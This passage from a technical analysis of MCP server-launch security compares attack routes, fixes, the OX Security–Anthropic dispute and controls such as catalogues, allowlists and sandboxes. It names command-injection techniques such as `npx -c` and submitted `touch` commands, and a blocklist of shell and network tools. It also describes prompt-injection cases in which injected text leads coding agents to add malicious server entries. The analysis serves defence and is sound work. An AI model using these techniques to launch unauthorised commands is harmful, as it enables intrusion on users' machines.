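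OX Security claims that a single change to the official SDKs would protect every downstream project. According to the graph, a check in the SDK's launch function would miss the sign-in route. It would also miss applications that don't use an official SDK, which make up about a fifth of the open-source applications that Majeed and colleagues studied.

The last link needs a check that can distinguish an attack from an ordinary launch, because removing the link would disable every local server. This is hardest for packages, where a malicious update like the one to `postmark-mcp` leaves the launch entry unchanged, so the check also has to verify the package's contents.

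### Complete mediation

A check that no path can avoid provides complete mediation, one of eight design principles in Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975). They state it as "Every access to every object must be checked for authority."

Several flaws in agent products violate conditions that Saltzer and Schroeder attached to complete mediation, the principle that every access must be checked. They wanted the check to apply during start-up and recovery as well as normal use. This matters for coding assistants because they start their servers before the user types anything, and a client may restart a server that has crashed. Saltzer and Schroeder also required a reliable way to identify the source of every request, but the early MCP Inspector could not distinguish requests from its own page from those sent by another website. They were sceptical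 of saving time by remembering an earlier decision, because the system must update that decision when the authority changes. Cursor remembered that a user had approved a server's name and then ran a different command under that name.

Recent work applies the principle of complete mediation to agents. *AgentKernel* (2026), a design for a trusted layer beneath agents, requires that an agent reach its tools and files only through the checked path. A coding assistant breaks this rule if its file editor refuses to change `mcp.json` but its terminal can overwrite it. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) assumes complete mediation in its mathematical proofs about agent security. The proofs apply only if the model reaches tools and untrusted sources through a monitor, so they don't apply if the agent runs a browser outside that monitor.

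### What each fix blocks

The table compares six common fixes with the six routes. The entries are judgements based on the published cases, not test results. "Partly" means the fix stops some attacks on that route.

| Fix | Web form | Injected text | Repository file | Package | Sign-in address | Web page to local service |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Login | Partly | No | No | No | No | Partly |
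| Command filter in the web application | Partly | No | No | No | No | Partly |
| Configuration the agent can't write | No | Yes | No | No | No | No |
| Approval tied to a hash of the entry | No | Partly | Partly | No | No | No |
| Registry vetting | No | No | No | Partly | No | No |
| Safe address opening | No | No | No | No | Yes | No |

A login keeps strangers away from a web form, but not people who have an account or can create one. On a local service, a script in the service's own page may steal the login token. A login also doesn't stop injected text, because the assistant is already working in the user's session.

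A command filter in a web application checks what people submit to that application, but it does not check the files that a coding assistant reads on a laptop. It protects even the web form only partially, because attackers can misuse permitted programs such as `npx`.

If write protection covers every way the agent can write files, including the terminal, it stops injected text from adding a launch entry. It doesn't stop a malicious repository file, because Git puts that file on the disk. It also doesn't stop an entry submitted through a web framework's form, because the framework saves the entry without involving an agent.

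With hash approval, the client asks the user before starting any entry whose hash has not been approved. If injected text adds an entry, the protection depends on the user reading the entry and refusing it. For entries in repository files, the hash catches only changes made after approval. If an entry is submitted through a web form, the attacker may be the person who receives the approval prompt.

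**Registry vetting.** A registry can reject a package that is already malicious, but not one that turns malicious later.

In 27 of the 36 combinations of fix and route, the fix does not help, and no fix helps on more than two routes. A company that adopted all six fixes would have some protection on every route but would fully block only two.

In *MCP-38*, Shen, Toyoda and Leung (2026) sort a much longer list of 38 threats to MCP systems into five categories by the kind of countermeasure each needs. For example, they recommend isolating outside content to counter prompt injection, and signing and verifying packages to counter supply-chain attacks. They split a threat in two if its variants required different countermeasures, so their list isn't independent proof that every route needs its own fix.

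### Two addresses that ran the same code

Langflow's developers closed one path to an operation but left another path to the same operation open. This case involves Python code rather than an MCP launch.

Langflow's `/api/v1/validate/code` endpoint accepted Python code from anyone and passed it to `exec()`, which runs text as code. Criminals used this flaw, CVE-2025-3248, in automated attacks. Langflow's developers responded by requiring a login at that endpoint.

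A researcher writing on HackerNoon then found that another address passed visitors' code to the same function, again without a sandbox. That address lets the public run flows that a Langflow user has shared, so requiring a login would have defeated its purpose. According to OSV's *Langflow has Unauthenticated Remote Code Execution via Public Flow Build Endpoint*, a visitor could submit a flow to use in place of the stored one, and Langflow would run the Python code in it. This second flaw, CVE-2026-33017, affects versions before 1.9.0. A sandbox around `exec()` could have limited the damage from both flaws.

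A fix can also fail to close the route it was meant to close. *MCP as the New Attack Surface* (Trent, 2026) describes an IBM bulletin from 28 October about Langflow's automatic login. Earlier fixes had shortened the lifetime of the tokens, but versions up to 1.12.8 still gave a superuser session to anyone who requested one, so an attacker could request a new token when the old one expired.

### An illustrative calculation

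As an invented example, suppose an organisation has four open routes, an attacker has a 10% chance of success on each, and the result on one doesn't affect the chances on another.

The chance that all four attempts fail is 0.9 × 0.9 × 0.9 × 0.9, or 65.6%, so the chance that at least one succeeds is 34.4%. A shared control that stops 90% of otherwise successful attempts on every route reduces each route's chance of success from 10% to 1%.

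| Defence | Calculation | Chance of at least one success |
|---|---|---|
| All four routes open | 1 − 0.9⁴ | 34.4% |
| One route closed | 1 − 0.9³ | 27.1% |
| Three routes closed | 1 − 0.9 | 10.0% |
| All four open behind the shared control | 1 − 0.99⁴ | 3.9% |

In this example, the imperfect shared control is more useful than closing three routes completely. Even a shared control that stopped only 24% of attempts would be about as useful as closing one route completely.

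#### When the routes are not independent

The benefit of closing one route may be even smaller if the same weakness makes every route work. Suppose one developer in ten approves whatever appears on the screen and the other nine never fall for an attack. An attacker who picks a developer at random has a 10% chance of success with four routes open. The chance stays at 10% until the company closes the last route, because the attacker can use any route that is still open.

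A shared control that doesn't rely on the developer's judgement still helps. If it stops 90% of attempts, the chance that a single attempt succeeds falls to 1%. For an attacker who tries all four routes, the chance of success is 3.4% if the control fails independently on each attempt.

Real attackers can't always switch routes so easily. Almost anyone can open a pull request on a public project, but far fewer people can publish an update to a package that the company already uses. Routes also differ in difficulty. If a web form gave an attacker a 40% chance of success and every other route gave 10%, closing the form would reduce the attacker's best chance from 40% to 10%. A company with limited time should therefore start with the route that is easiest to attack.

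### Evidence from existing defences

In *MCP-DPT*, Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues (2026) examined how much of an MCP system current security products can protect. They collected 49 attacks from published research and assigned each to the part of the system that could stop it earliest. They then judged, from the designs of 13 defences, which attacks each could detect, block or limit. They did not run the attacks, so an attack counted as covered might still succeed in practice.

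| Part of the system | Attacks assigned to it | Highest coverage by one defence |
|---|---|---|
| Model | 9 | 44% |
| Application | 13 | 38% |
| Client or SDK | 11 | 36% |
| Server | 6 | 50% |
| Network transport | 4 | 50% |
| Registry and supply chain | 6 | 100% |

The application and the client or SDK handle launches. Nearly half of the attacks, 24 of 49, belong to these two parts, and the best defences for them cover a smaller share of attacks than the best defences for the other parts. No defence covers more than half of the attacks in more than one part of the system. ToolHive, for example, covers 100% of the registry attacks but only 23% of the application attacks and 9% of the client attacks. A company that used it against poisoned packages would still need other protection for its launch configurations.

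Only one of the 13 defences, MCP-Guard, covers "Command Execution" and "Remote Code Execution", the two attacks in the study that are closest to a malicious launch.

The percentages are rough. Rostamzadeh and colleagues write that every defence except MCP-Gateway scores zero on network transport, but their table gives two others 25%. Many of the 49 attacks, such as getting a model to reveal its hidden instructions, don't involve starting a process. The study supports the claim that existing defences are narrow, but it doesn't measure how often attackers switch routes when a company closes one.

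The researchers favour stopping each attack as early as possible, while the graph suggests a later point that many attacks share. The two approaches can work together because the study also identifies a fallback point for stopping each attack. In its example, a registry approves a harmless tool that later becomes malicious, and the application, unlike the registry, can detect the change when the tool runs.

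### Evidence from published vulnerabilities

A study by He and colleagues provides a different test because it examined flaws that researchers had found in real products. They searched the CVE database for "MCP" and "Model Context Protocol" and retrieved 119 records published between January 2025 and February 2026. Removing duplicates and invalid entries left 108. They then excluded 72 in which "MCP" meant something else, 8 that mentioned the protocol only in passing and 4 that were incomplete or unconfirmed, which left 24 vulnerabilities.

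The researchers rated 14 of the 24 flaws critical, 7 high, 2 medium and 1 low. They attributed 11 to servers, 8 to clients and 5 to SDKs. Sixteen involve command injection, remote code execution or path traversal, which lets an attacker reach files outside a permitted folder.

These categories don't record how an attacker reached the vulnerable code, so we can't use the totals to test the graph directly. The individual cases are more useful, and at least four of them involve launch configurations. He et al. class one of the four as a server (Flowise), two as clients (LibreChat and Dive) and one as an SDK (WeKnora), so someone who looked only at the totals could miss that all four have a similar weakness.

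Dive, a desktop application that manages MCP servers, had a route that is not among the six in the graph. Before version 0.13.0, an attacker could put a server configuration into a special link. If the user opened it, Dive could add the attacker's server or replace an existing one without adequate confirmation. Protecting the configuration file from an AI agent would not have helped, because Dive itself made the change. A check on every new launch could have covered this route even if its designers had not anticipated such links.

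Access control seems to matter more for launches than for MCP vulnerabilities in general. He et al. found inadequate access control in 4 of the 24 cases, and 3 of those 4 were in Flowise, LibreChat and Dive. These numbers are too small to establish a general rate.

The dataset also includes a shared fix. The official TypeScript SDK originally left its protection against DNS rebinding off. Version 1.24.0 turned it on, which protected applications built on the SDK once their developers updated. He and colleagues argue that the same flaw will keep returning if each application has to add such a protection separately.

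Of the 24 records, 20 give only the year of disclosure, so the dataset can't show whether attackers or researchers moved to a new route after a patch. It also covers only published flaws, not actual attacks. Together, the two studies moderately support the claim that fixing one route leaves others open. Langflow is more direct evidence, but it is only one case.

### When one fix may be enough

Some systems have only one route that an attacker can realistically reach. For example, a web application might run one local server from a reviewed copy with fixed dependencies, read no project files, connect to no remote servers and have no agent that can change its settings. If only a web form can change the launch configuration, limiting that form to trusted administrators may be enough.

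The owner has to confirm that no other route exists. Cantina advises tracing where `command`, `args`, `cwd` and `env` come from, and treating web requests, model output, configuration files and database entries as untrusted until someone checks them. It also warns that companies often review prompt injection, local configuration and laptop security separately, so nobody notices a path that runs through all three. Cantina sells this kind of review, but a developer can do a basic version by searching the code.

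Installing new software can open another route. One flaw in Langflow let users write launch entries for coding assistants on the same machine, so adding a coding assistant to a Langflow server would have created a route in addition to the server's web form.

### When a shared control fails

A flaw in a shared control can leave every route open at once. Saltzer and Schroeder recognised this risk in another principle, least common mechanism, under which designers minimise the parts of a system that all users depend on. They argued that a shared part must satisfy every user, which is harder than satisfying one or a few. They also recommended keeping protection mechanisms small and simple enough to inspect line by line.

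Developers can also overestimate how much a control covers. *Governed MCP* (2026) describes a gateway that checks agents' tool calls in an experimental operating system. Its author originally claimed that the system checked all 123 paths from an agent to the rest of the system. The author withdrew that claim in July 2026, after a recount with a new test found 59 paths, of which the system checked 43. The gateway still covered all MCP tool calls, but six known paths through system calls had no check.

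The calculation above optimistically assumes that the shared control stops 90% of attempts whatever the attacker does. Once attackers know a bypass that always works, the control stops nothing, and their chance of success returns to 34.4%. Fixes for individual routes still help in that case. If the company had also closed one of the four routes, the chance would be 3.0% while the shared control worked and 27.1% after it failed.

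## Whether the protocol or the application should restrict launches

Most ways of launching a program locally go through the SDK's launch function, so it is the obvious place for a shared check. In January 2026, OX Security asked Anthropic to restrict launches there. Anthropic declined because it considers starting a chosen program to be the function's purpose and expects applications to control who chooses the program.

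### How the dispute began

OX's researchers began their work in November 2025, according to VentureBeat's *200,000 MCP servers expose a command execution flaw*. They first saw the problem in GPT Researcher, whose web page let users supply the command for a stdio server. ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector for supply chain* reports that any command they entered ran on the server, even when no MCP server started. GPT Researcher used LangChain's older adapter, so the researchers assumed the adapter was at fault. They then found that it only passed the values on, and that the official SDK launched the command.

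LangChain and Anthropic both told OX that this was expected behaviour. flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report*, a blog post that quotes the replies, dates OX's first contact with Anthropic to 7 January 2026. LangChain answered that application authors must validate untrusted input. FastMCP's maintainers pointed out that, under the MCP specification, the client starts a subprocess. Anthropic replied that "this design does represent a secure default".

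Nine days after OX Security's first contact, Anthropic added a note to the project's security policy that developers should use stdio adapters with caution, but it did not change the code. Anthropic raised no objection when OX said it planned to publish, and OX released the report on 15 April 2026. By then OX had sent more than 30 reports to projects that use MCP. OX names 13 projects whose maintainers rejected its findings, including tools from Amazon and NVIDIA.

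OX lists CVEs for applications such as LiteLLM and Windsurf, but none for the official SDKs. A vulnerability scanner that relies on CVEs can therefore flag an old copy of LiteLLM, but it won't flag a new application that passes untrusted text to the current SDK. Assigning the CVEs to applications has also caused some confusion. For example, the *MCP Security* page in the llmist framework's documentation describes CVE-2026-30623 as a flaw in four official SDKs, but that CVE is for LiteLLM.

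### Which report Anthropic's "user permission" reply answers

Press coverage has mixed up two of Anthropic's replies. ITPro quotes Anthropic as rejecting the vulnerability because "it requires explicit user permission for the file change". ITPro places this quotation after its account of the SDK report, so readers would likely take it as Anthropic's defence of the SDK.

That reading makes little sense, because the SDK's launch function doesn't edit a configuration file or show an approval prompt. In the Langflow attack, a stranger submits a form and the server runs the command, so no legitimate user has a chance to refuse.

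Anthropic was almost certainly answering OX's report about Claude Code with this reply, although ITPro does not specify which report it was. The reply matches the reason coding-assistant vendors gave for rejecting OX's reports about edited configuration files, and Cursor's was almost identical. The "secure default" reply concerns the SDK.

Both quotations come from Anthropic's correspondence with OX. According to VentureBeat, "expected" is the only word Anthropic has said on the record, and the company did not respond to VentureBeat's request for comment.

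### The argument for a change in the SDKs

OX argues that the people who build on MCP can't be expected to find this danger themselves. Its researchers told ITPro that "developers are not security engineers". These developers trust an official library, which contains no warning that `command` will run whatever text it receives.

The number of affected products supports this. Developers of about a dozen frameworks independently built a form that let users run commands on the server. CSO Online's *RCE by design* (2026) reports that few developers had tried to filter the commands, and that OX bypassed the filters of those who had. Carter Rees, an AI executive at the company Reputation, told VentureBeat that a failure repeated across so many independent products is no longer a developer's mistake.

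OX also expects the problem to grow as more people build software with AI assistants. In bdtechtalks' *The 'by design' security flaw of Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, OX's research lead, Moshe Siman Tov Bustan, argues that if the AI doesn't question the library it is using, the developer won't either.

The official TypeScript SDK sets a good precedent for a shared fix. It now protects against DNS rebinding by default and rejects dangerous sign-in addresses, both of which the maintainers could have left to applications.

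However, OX goes too far when it claims that a change would "instantly" protect everyone downstream. Developers would first have to update the SDK in their applications, and users might then have to update those applications. The number of people who would benefit is also unclear. flyingpenguin reports 73 million downloads for the Python SDK, 57 million for LiteLLM and 22 million for FastMCP. These total 152 million, which is probably the source of OX's headline figure of more than 150 million. LiteLLM and FastMCP both depend on the SDK, so one installation can be counted twice.

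OX Security has a commercial interest in the dispute. In the same post as its findings, it announced that its products now detect code that passes user input into a stdio configuration. This is a reason for caution about phrases such as "the mother of all AI supply chains", but it doesn't weaken the technical evidence, since anyone can check that the SDK starts `touch`.

### The argument for leaving the choice to applications

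VentureBeat has explained Anthropic's position more fully than Anthropic has publicly. The stdio transport exists to start local programs, and whoever controls the configuration decides which ones. On this view, anyone allowed to edit that configuration is already allowed to run commands on the machine. If the SDK permitted only certain programs, it would either break legitimate servers or lead attackers to use the programs it still permitted. Because the standard is meant for every kind of tool, Anthropic also can't know in advance which programs users will need.

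The MCP maintainers describe the STDIO transport as bluntly as OX does. Cantina quotes their meeting notes of 31 March 2026, two weeks before OX published: "STDIO = arbitrary local binary execution." The project's position, in its security guidance, is that the transport "is not inherently vulnerable".

The best technical argument for leaving restrictions to the application is that the SDK has no information about where a command came from. A value in `StdioServerParameters` is just text, and `npx` looks the same whether the user typed it, a stranger submitted it through a form or a model copied it from a web page. Only the application has access to the source, so only the application can decide whether to trust the command. Python's `subprocess` module and the operating system's `execve` call don't make that decision either.

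Being able to edit the configuration often doesn't mean having permission to run commands. A user on their own laptop has that permission, but a visitor to an open Langflow server, a website that gets Windsurf to edit its server list, or a stranger whose pull request contains an `.mcp.json` file does not. Anthropic could reply that those applications were wrong to let outsiders reach the configuration, and the CVEs do mostly attribute the vulnerabilities to the applications. That reply would be more persuasive if the security policy had advised caution from the start, rather than after OX's report.

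### Older tools with the same design

Hirschberg, of ARMO, accepts OX's technical findings but rejects the idea that MCP has a special flaw, and backs this up with older tools.

The closest match is Jupyter, a program that data scientists use to run code in notebooks. Jupyter searches known folders for files called `kernel.json`, which contain command arguments and environment variables. It starts the program named in the file without checking what it is. The format dates from about 2015, and Hirschberg writes that nobody has called it a critical vulnerability.

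Development containers, which give a project a ready-made environment to run in, have an `initializeCommand` setting that runs a command on the developer's own machine, outside the container. According to Hirschberg, no trust prompt protects this setting, which would make it riskier than an MCP entry in Cursor or Claude Desktop.

Git runs scripts called hooks at certain moments, such as after a checkout. Hirschberg doesn't consider this a vulnerability. CVE-2024-32002 was a vulnerability because an outsider could write a script into the hooks folder when a user cloned a crafted repository. Hirschberg wants people to make the same distinction for MCP, between running configured commands and letting an outsider add them.

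The comparison with Git is useful but inexact, because Git is an application and the MCP SDK is a library. Git's developers decide how a hook can get onto a user's machine, just as Cursor's developers decide who can edit `mcp.json`. The Git example therefore supports Anthropic's view that applications have to guard the configuration.

Hirschberg also rates MCP's protection as medium because Claude Desktop and Cursor require approval for each server, as well as a restart. This reasoning doesn't cover most of what OX found. Nine of the ten CVEs in OX's announcement concern agent frameworks and web applications, many of which had no approval step. The tenth concerns a coding assistant, Windsurf, which started the new server immediately.

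Hirschberg then concedes that all these older formats assume a person will look at the file before a tool runs it, and that a coding agent can break that assumption. Injected text could make an agent write an MCP entry, a development container setting or an npm installation script. It could also make the agent put a program in Docker's plugin folder, which would run the next time the developer used the matching Docker command. He concludes that all of these files need stronger protection.

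This weakens the case for relying on an SDK change, because an attacker who controls the agent's edits could use one of the other files instead. The change could still help against a stranger filling in a web form, who usually can't write to those files.

ARMO has a commercial interest too. Hirschberg recommends watching which processes start other processes, and ARMO sells runtime detection of that kind. The flyingpenguin blogger promotes Wirken, an agent gateway he built.

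### OX's proposals against the documented attacks

OX proposed three changes to the way the SDKs launch programs: a flag that marks unsafe use, a default list of permitted commands, and a requirement that programs launch only from a declared manifest. The table shows the likely effect of each change in seven cases. The entries are judgements based on how each attack worked, because OX has not published a test of the changes against these cases.

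| Attack | Unsafe-use flag | Default allowlist that includes `npx` | Declared manifest |
|---|---|---|---|
| Langflow: visitor submits a command | Unlikely to stop it | Stops `touch`, but not `npx -c` | Stops it if visitors can't edit the manifest |
| Flowise: `npx -c` | Unlikely to stop it | No effect | Stops it if the manifest fixes the arguments |
| Letta: stdio option missing from the page | Might stop it | Stops `touch`, but not `npx -c` | Stops it if users can't edit the manifest |
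| Windsurf: injected text adds a server | No effect | Stops only programs not on the list | Stops it if the agent can't edit the manifest |
| Claude Code: pull request adds `.mcp.json` | No effect | Stops only programs not on the list | Stops it if the manifest comes from elsewhere |
| `postmark-mcp`: malicious update | No effect | No effect | No effect |
| OpenCode: malicious sign-in address | No effect | No effect | No effect |

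#### A flag for unsafe use

Bustan proposes that the SDK block arbitrary commands unless the developer passes a flag whose name makes the danger clear. OX Security suggests `allow_unsafe_command_execution=True`.

Deciding when to require the flag is difficult. flyingpenguin describes the proposal as a flag for configurations with dynamic arguments, meaning values that can change while the program runs. The SDK can't recognise dynamic arguments, because it receives a fixed string and a user's string in the same form. It would have to require the flag for every launch outside some approved set. OX's own example sets the flag on an ordinary entry that runs `python` with `myapp.py`. If harmless programs need the flag, developers will copy it from the tutorial and stop noticing it.

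Langflow and Flowise deliberately let users add their own servers, so their developers would presumably have set the flag. Developers of coding assistants would also have to set it so that users could install new servers. The flag is most likely to have helped in Letta's case, because Letta's web page wasn't supposed to offer stdio. If nobody had set the flag in the code behind that page, OX's altered request would have failed.

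The flag would also help code reviewers, who could search for it and check where each command came from. This is easier than finding every indirect use of the SDK. The flag would give developers a warning they can't miss, but it wouldn't stop an attacker once developers had accepted that warning.

#### A default list of permitted commands

The reports use "allowlist" for two different rules. An allowlist permits named programs and refuses the rest, but according to CSO Online, OX wants an "allowlist" that blocks `sh`, `bash`, `powershell`, `curl`, `rm` and other high-risk programs. That is a blocklist, which would fail if it omitted one dangerous program, such as `npx`.

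A true allowlist would be stronger, but the SDK's maintainers would have to decide whether to allow `npx`, as Flowise's developers had to. If they left it out, most applications would probably disable the list or add `npx` themselves.

In its own account of the Flowise bypass, OX calls ad hoc filtering an insufficient defence when the design permits any subprocess. The same criticism applies to an SDK list that checks only the program's name. One advantage of a central list would be that the maintainers could fix a newly discovered bypass once for every application that updates.

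#### Launches only from a declared manifest

With manifest-only execution, the application starts only servers that somebody has already defined in a fixed file. A user's request contains a server's name and no command:

```json
{"server": "filesystem"}
```

The application looks up `filesystem` and starts the program in its entry. A visitor who sent `touch` would get an error, because no server has that name. OX's trick with Letta would fail too, since the application would ignore any `command` field in the request.

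For web applications, this is the strongest of the three proposals, as long as users can't change the rest of the entry. But some servers need a value from the user, such as the folder that Maria's server may read. If the request can supply arguments, the application has to check them, or an attacker can try argument injection again.

The proposal does much less for coding assistants. They already start their servers from a file, and a manifest protects users only if an attacker can't write to it. In Windsurf's case, the agent could edit that file. A repository's `.mcp.json` also declares a list of servers, but an attacker may have written it.

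The SDK can't prevent a developer who wants to let users add any server from saving their text to the manifest and then having the SDK start the new entry. But the developer would have to do this deliberately, whereas today passing a user's text straight to the launch function takes one line of code.

Cantina recommends a catalogue of approved servers from which the user picks one, while the platform supplies the command. Developers can adopt this design without waiting for the SDK to do so. This makes OX's demand somewhat less urgent, but only for developers who know about the danger, and OX complains that many don't.

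A reasonable compromise would be for the SDK to launch tools by name by default and accept free-form commands only through a separate function whose name clearly warns of the danger. Applications that need to start any program could still do so, and developers who had never thought about the danger would be less likely to expose that ability by accident.

#### What none of these changes checks

None of the three SDK changes examines the contents of a package, so the malicious version of `postmark-mcp` would have passed all of them.

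OX's fourth proposal covers the marketplaces. According to flyingpenguin, publishers would have to prove their identity and sign a security manifest for each server. According to bdtechtalks, the manifest would list the network addresses and files the server needs. This could expose a calculator whose manifest lists SSH keys. It probably wouldn't have caught `postmark-mcp`, which needed no connection beyond the one to Postmark. The manifest also wouldn't restrict a running server unless a sandbox enforced it.

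bdtechtalks gives some details of OX's registry trial that the company's own summary leaves out. LobeHub and Cursor Directory were among the nine that published the harmless test entry without a security review. GitHub was the only one to reject it, and Cline never responded. This gives some support to OX's advice to use GitHub's registry, though a single rejected entry is thin evidence of how well GitHub checks the rest.

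### The current MCP policy

The project has kept its position since April. The SDK's launch function still accepts any program name, although the July 2026 revision would have been a convenient time for a breaking change.

The Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy* now states that the SDK is not responsible for protecting a client from a malicious stdio server, because a server that is already running can execute code anyway. The SDK is also not responsible for protecting a server from a malicious client, because the client controls the server's process. Anyone who runs stdio servers with reduced privileges has to enforce those restrictions separately, since the transport "is not a sandbox".

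The policy still accepts reports of injection bugs in the SDKs. That would presumably include an SDK that turned a harmless argument into a second command, but not one that correctly started the program an application had named. This distinction is sensible for two programs that are already connected, but it doesn't address OX's main concern, which is how an outsider came to choose the program.

The separate security guidance requires a client that offers one-click installation to show the user the full command and get approval before running it, but only recommends a sandbox. The application that contains the client is responsible for both measures, and the SDK enforces neither.

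OX directed its demands at Anthropic, but Anthropic had donated MCP a month before OX made contact, so the project's maintainers would presumably have to agree to any change to the SDKs. When someone reports a vulnerability in one official SDK, its maintainers check whether the others share it so that they can release the fixes together. OX's report didn't lead to a joint fix because the maintainers don't regard the launch behaviour as a vulnerability.

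## Controls at the point of launch

The official SDKs start whatever program they are given, so a company that wants a check on every launch has to add one or use a product that includes one. The best place for the check is just before the operating system creates the process, because all six routes pass through that point.

### A catalogue of approved servers

With a catalogue, the user or the model picks only a server's identifier, and the platform supplies everything else. An administrator writes each entry in advance. An entry for an invented notes server could look like this:

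```json
{
  "notes": {
    "version": "1.4.2",
    "package": "/opt/mcp/notes-1.4.2.tar",
    "sha256": "9f2c...",
    "program": "/opt/node/bin/node",
    "args": ["index.js"],
    "env": {"LOG_LEVEL": "info"},
    "folders": ["/workspace"],
    "hosts": ["api.notes.example"]
  }
}
```

The archive named in `package` contains the server and all its dependencies, so one hash covers code that `npx` would otherwise download at launch. `program` gives the full path to Node.js, so an attacker can't use `PATH` to substitute a different program. The last two fields set limits for a sandbox.

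Before each launch, the platform runs a check like this:

```
launch(user, server_id):
    entry = catalogue.find(server_id)
    if there is no entry, or user may not use it: refuse
    copy = private_copy(entry.package)
    if sha256(copy) != entry.sha256: refuse
    code = unpack(copy)
    box = sandbox(code, entry.folders, entry.hosts)
    log(user, server_id, entry.sha256)
    box.start(entry.program, entry.args, entry.env, code)
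```

As with OX's declared manifest, the request contains no command, arguments or environment variables. The check copies the archive before hashing it, since an attacker could otherwise replace the file between the comparison and the launch. If the catalogue is unavailable, no tool starts.

This control stops `npx -c`, unfamiliar packages and updates that nobody has reviewed. It doesn't detect malicious code that the administrator approved, or a flaw in a non-malicious server. It also has no effect on software that starts processes without calling `launch`.

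If a server needs a value from the user, the platform can avoid accepting free text. For Maria's filesystem server, it can fill in her open project's folder or let her choose from a list.

Docker offers a partial version of this design. According to *MCP gateway*, a user can give Docker's `sbx` tool the address of a registry entry, and the tool finds and starts the container image named there. It will not launch npm packages this way, although the user can register an explicit command for them. The server's publisher wrote the registry entry, however, so a company using the tool still has to decide which entries to trust.

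### What companies can enforce in current products

Several coding assistants now let an administrator restrict MCP servers across a whole company. They differ in how they recognise an approved server.

Matching by name is the weakest method, because the user chooses the name. Cline compares the server's name in the user's configuration with a list of approved names, so a user could run any program by giving it an approved name, such as `github`. GitHub Copilot began with a similar rule that checked only the identifiers of local servers, according to GitHub's *Internal MCP registry and allowlist controls for VS Code Insiders* (2025). GitHub's *MCP allowlists in enterprise managed settings* (2026) describes a stronger method, generally available since August 2026, that compares the exact command and arguments.

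| Product and method | What a local server must match | Main gap |
|---|---|---|
| Copilot, managed settings | Command and arguments | Works only in the Copilot app, Copilot CLI and VS Code |
| Copilot, company registry | Name or identifier | Users can get around it by editing configuration files |
| Claude Code, allowlist | Command and every argument, in order | Ignores environment variables |
| Claude Code, `managed-mcp.json` | Nothing, because the administrator supplies the whole entry | Does not cover connectors that the desktop app delivers |
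| Codex | Name and command | Can run without the company's online policy |
| Amp | Package name and registry | Accepts any version |
| Cline | Name | Users can give any server an approved name |

The older registry method for Copilot is still available, but GitHub's *MCP server usage in your company* recommends managed settings instead.

Claude Code's allowlist, like Devin Desktop's, does not check the `env` field. In Anthropic's example, an approved `node server.js` matches whatever that field contains. An administrator can close this gap by putting complete server entries in `managed-mcp.json`, a file in a protected system folder. Claude Code then ignores servers that users, projects and plugins add.

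An administrator who prefers the allowlist also has to set `allowManagedMcpServersOnly`. Otherwise, Claude Code merges the company's list with the user's, so a user, or an agent that can edit the user's settings, could approve more servers.

The products also behave differently when they can't read the policy. Copilot blocks a configuration that it can't verify. Amp, another coding assistant, blocks every server if it can't reach the company's registry, according to Amp's *MCP Registry Allowlist*. According to OpenAI's *Managed configuration*, if Codex can't download a policy from OpenAI's online service and has no valid saved copy, it continues without the policy. A company can avoid depending on the download by also installing the rules in a system file on each machine.

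None of the matching rules in the table checks the contents of a package or its dependencies.

### Showing the user the full command

Individual users have no administrator to approve servers for them, so an approval prompt is often the only check. The MCP project's rule for these prompts is SEP-1024, one of its numbered proposals for changing the specification. Delimarsky (2025), in *MCP Client Security Requirements for Local Server Installation*, sets out what a client must do before a one-click installation:

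- show the exact command and all its arguments, without shortening them
- warn that the operation may be dangerous
- wait for the user to approve it, and offer a way to cancel

Requiring a client to show the command in a dialog before one-click installation stops an "Add to editor" button from hiding it. The rule covers only one-click installation, so a client can comply and still start an entry that came from a repository file or was written by an agent without showing its command. It also doesn't require the dialog to show environment variables or the working directory, so an attacker could use either to change the npm registry without the user seeing it.

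Even a complete prompt doesn't show what is in the package, so `npx -y postmark-mcp` would have looked harmless.

There is little evidence on how well people judge these prompts. *Model Context Protocol (MCP) Security* (2026), from the Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI), an industry group, warns of consent fatigue, in which users approve prompts by reflex, but gives no measurements. Huang, Huang and Milani Fard tested what the dialogs of seven clients displayed, but not what users decided. There seems to be no published experiment on whether people can tell harmful launch commands from harmless ones. Delimarsky accepts that users may approve malicious commands despite the warning, and recommends sandboxes and signatures as further protection.

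Trust settings can also remove the prompt. According to VS Code's November 2026 reference, MCP servers in a project inherit the trust the user gave the project's folder. The separate approval after a configuration change, described in Microsoft documentation that Mindgard quoted, may therefore no longer protect users when a server entry in a repository changes.

### Limiting what a started server can reach

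A sandbox is useful when every earlier check has failed, because it doesn't depend on anyone recognising the server as malicious. The launcher gives the operating system a list of permitted files and network addresses, and the system stops the server and any programs it starts from accessing anything else.

According to Anthropic, a sandbox has to limit access to both files and the network. If a malicious program can read SSH keys and connect anywhere, it can send the keys out. If it has no network access but can change any file, it may be able to alter something that runs outside the sandbox and get network access that way.

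VS Code lets users list the folders a sandboxed server may write to and the files it may not read. Its reference documents no setting that limits reading to listed files, so users have to think of every sensitive location themselves. A launcher that lets a server access only its own code and the current project is safer, because it also protects files that nobody thought to list.

**Network.** A notes server may need only one host. But it can still misuse that host, as `postmark-mcp` did with Postmark.

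**Environment variables.** The launcher should start with an empty environment and add only what the server needs.

**Credentials.** Copilot CLI, GitHub's terminal agent, can hide the real value of a password or token from a sandboxed server. According to GitHub's *Configuring local sandbox settings*, the server receives a placeholder, which a local proxy replaces with the real token when the server sends it to an approved host. The server never receives the real token, so it can't pass the token to an attacker. It can still do anything the token allows at the approved host, including deleting data.

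Default settings can leave gaps in a sandbox. Copilot CLI lets sandboxed commands read the settings of developer tools, including access tokens for package registries, unless the user turns this off. On Windows, its rules about permitted hosts work only if a program uses the proxy settings, and a malicious program can ignore those settings.

VS Code also stops asking users to confirm tool calls once a server is in a sandbox. This spares them many prompts but removes a check on actions the sandbox permits. For example, a sandboxed email server could send a message to the wrong person without the user seeing a prompt.

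#### Which assistants use a sandbox by default

Claude Code, GitHub Copilot and VS Code all have sandboxes, but none of them puts local MCP servers in one until a user or administrator turns it on.

| Product | Is the sandbox on by default? | Does it cover local MCP servers? |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | No | No, they run with the user's full access |
| Copilot CLI | No | Yes, unless the user turns this off |
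| VS Code | No, and unavailable on Windows | Only servers whose entry turns it on |

Claude Code's `/sandbox` setting confines only shell commands and the programs they start, according to Anthropic's October 2026 documentation. It doesn't confine MCP servers, but a developer who sees that Claude's commands can't write outside the project could assume that it does. To confine the servers too, the developer has to run all of Claude Code in a container or in Anthropic's separate sandbox runtime, as Anthropic describes.

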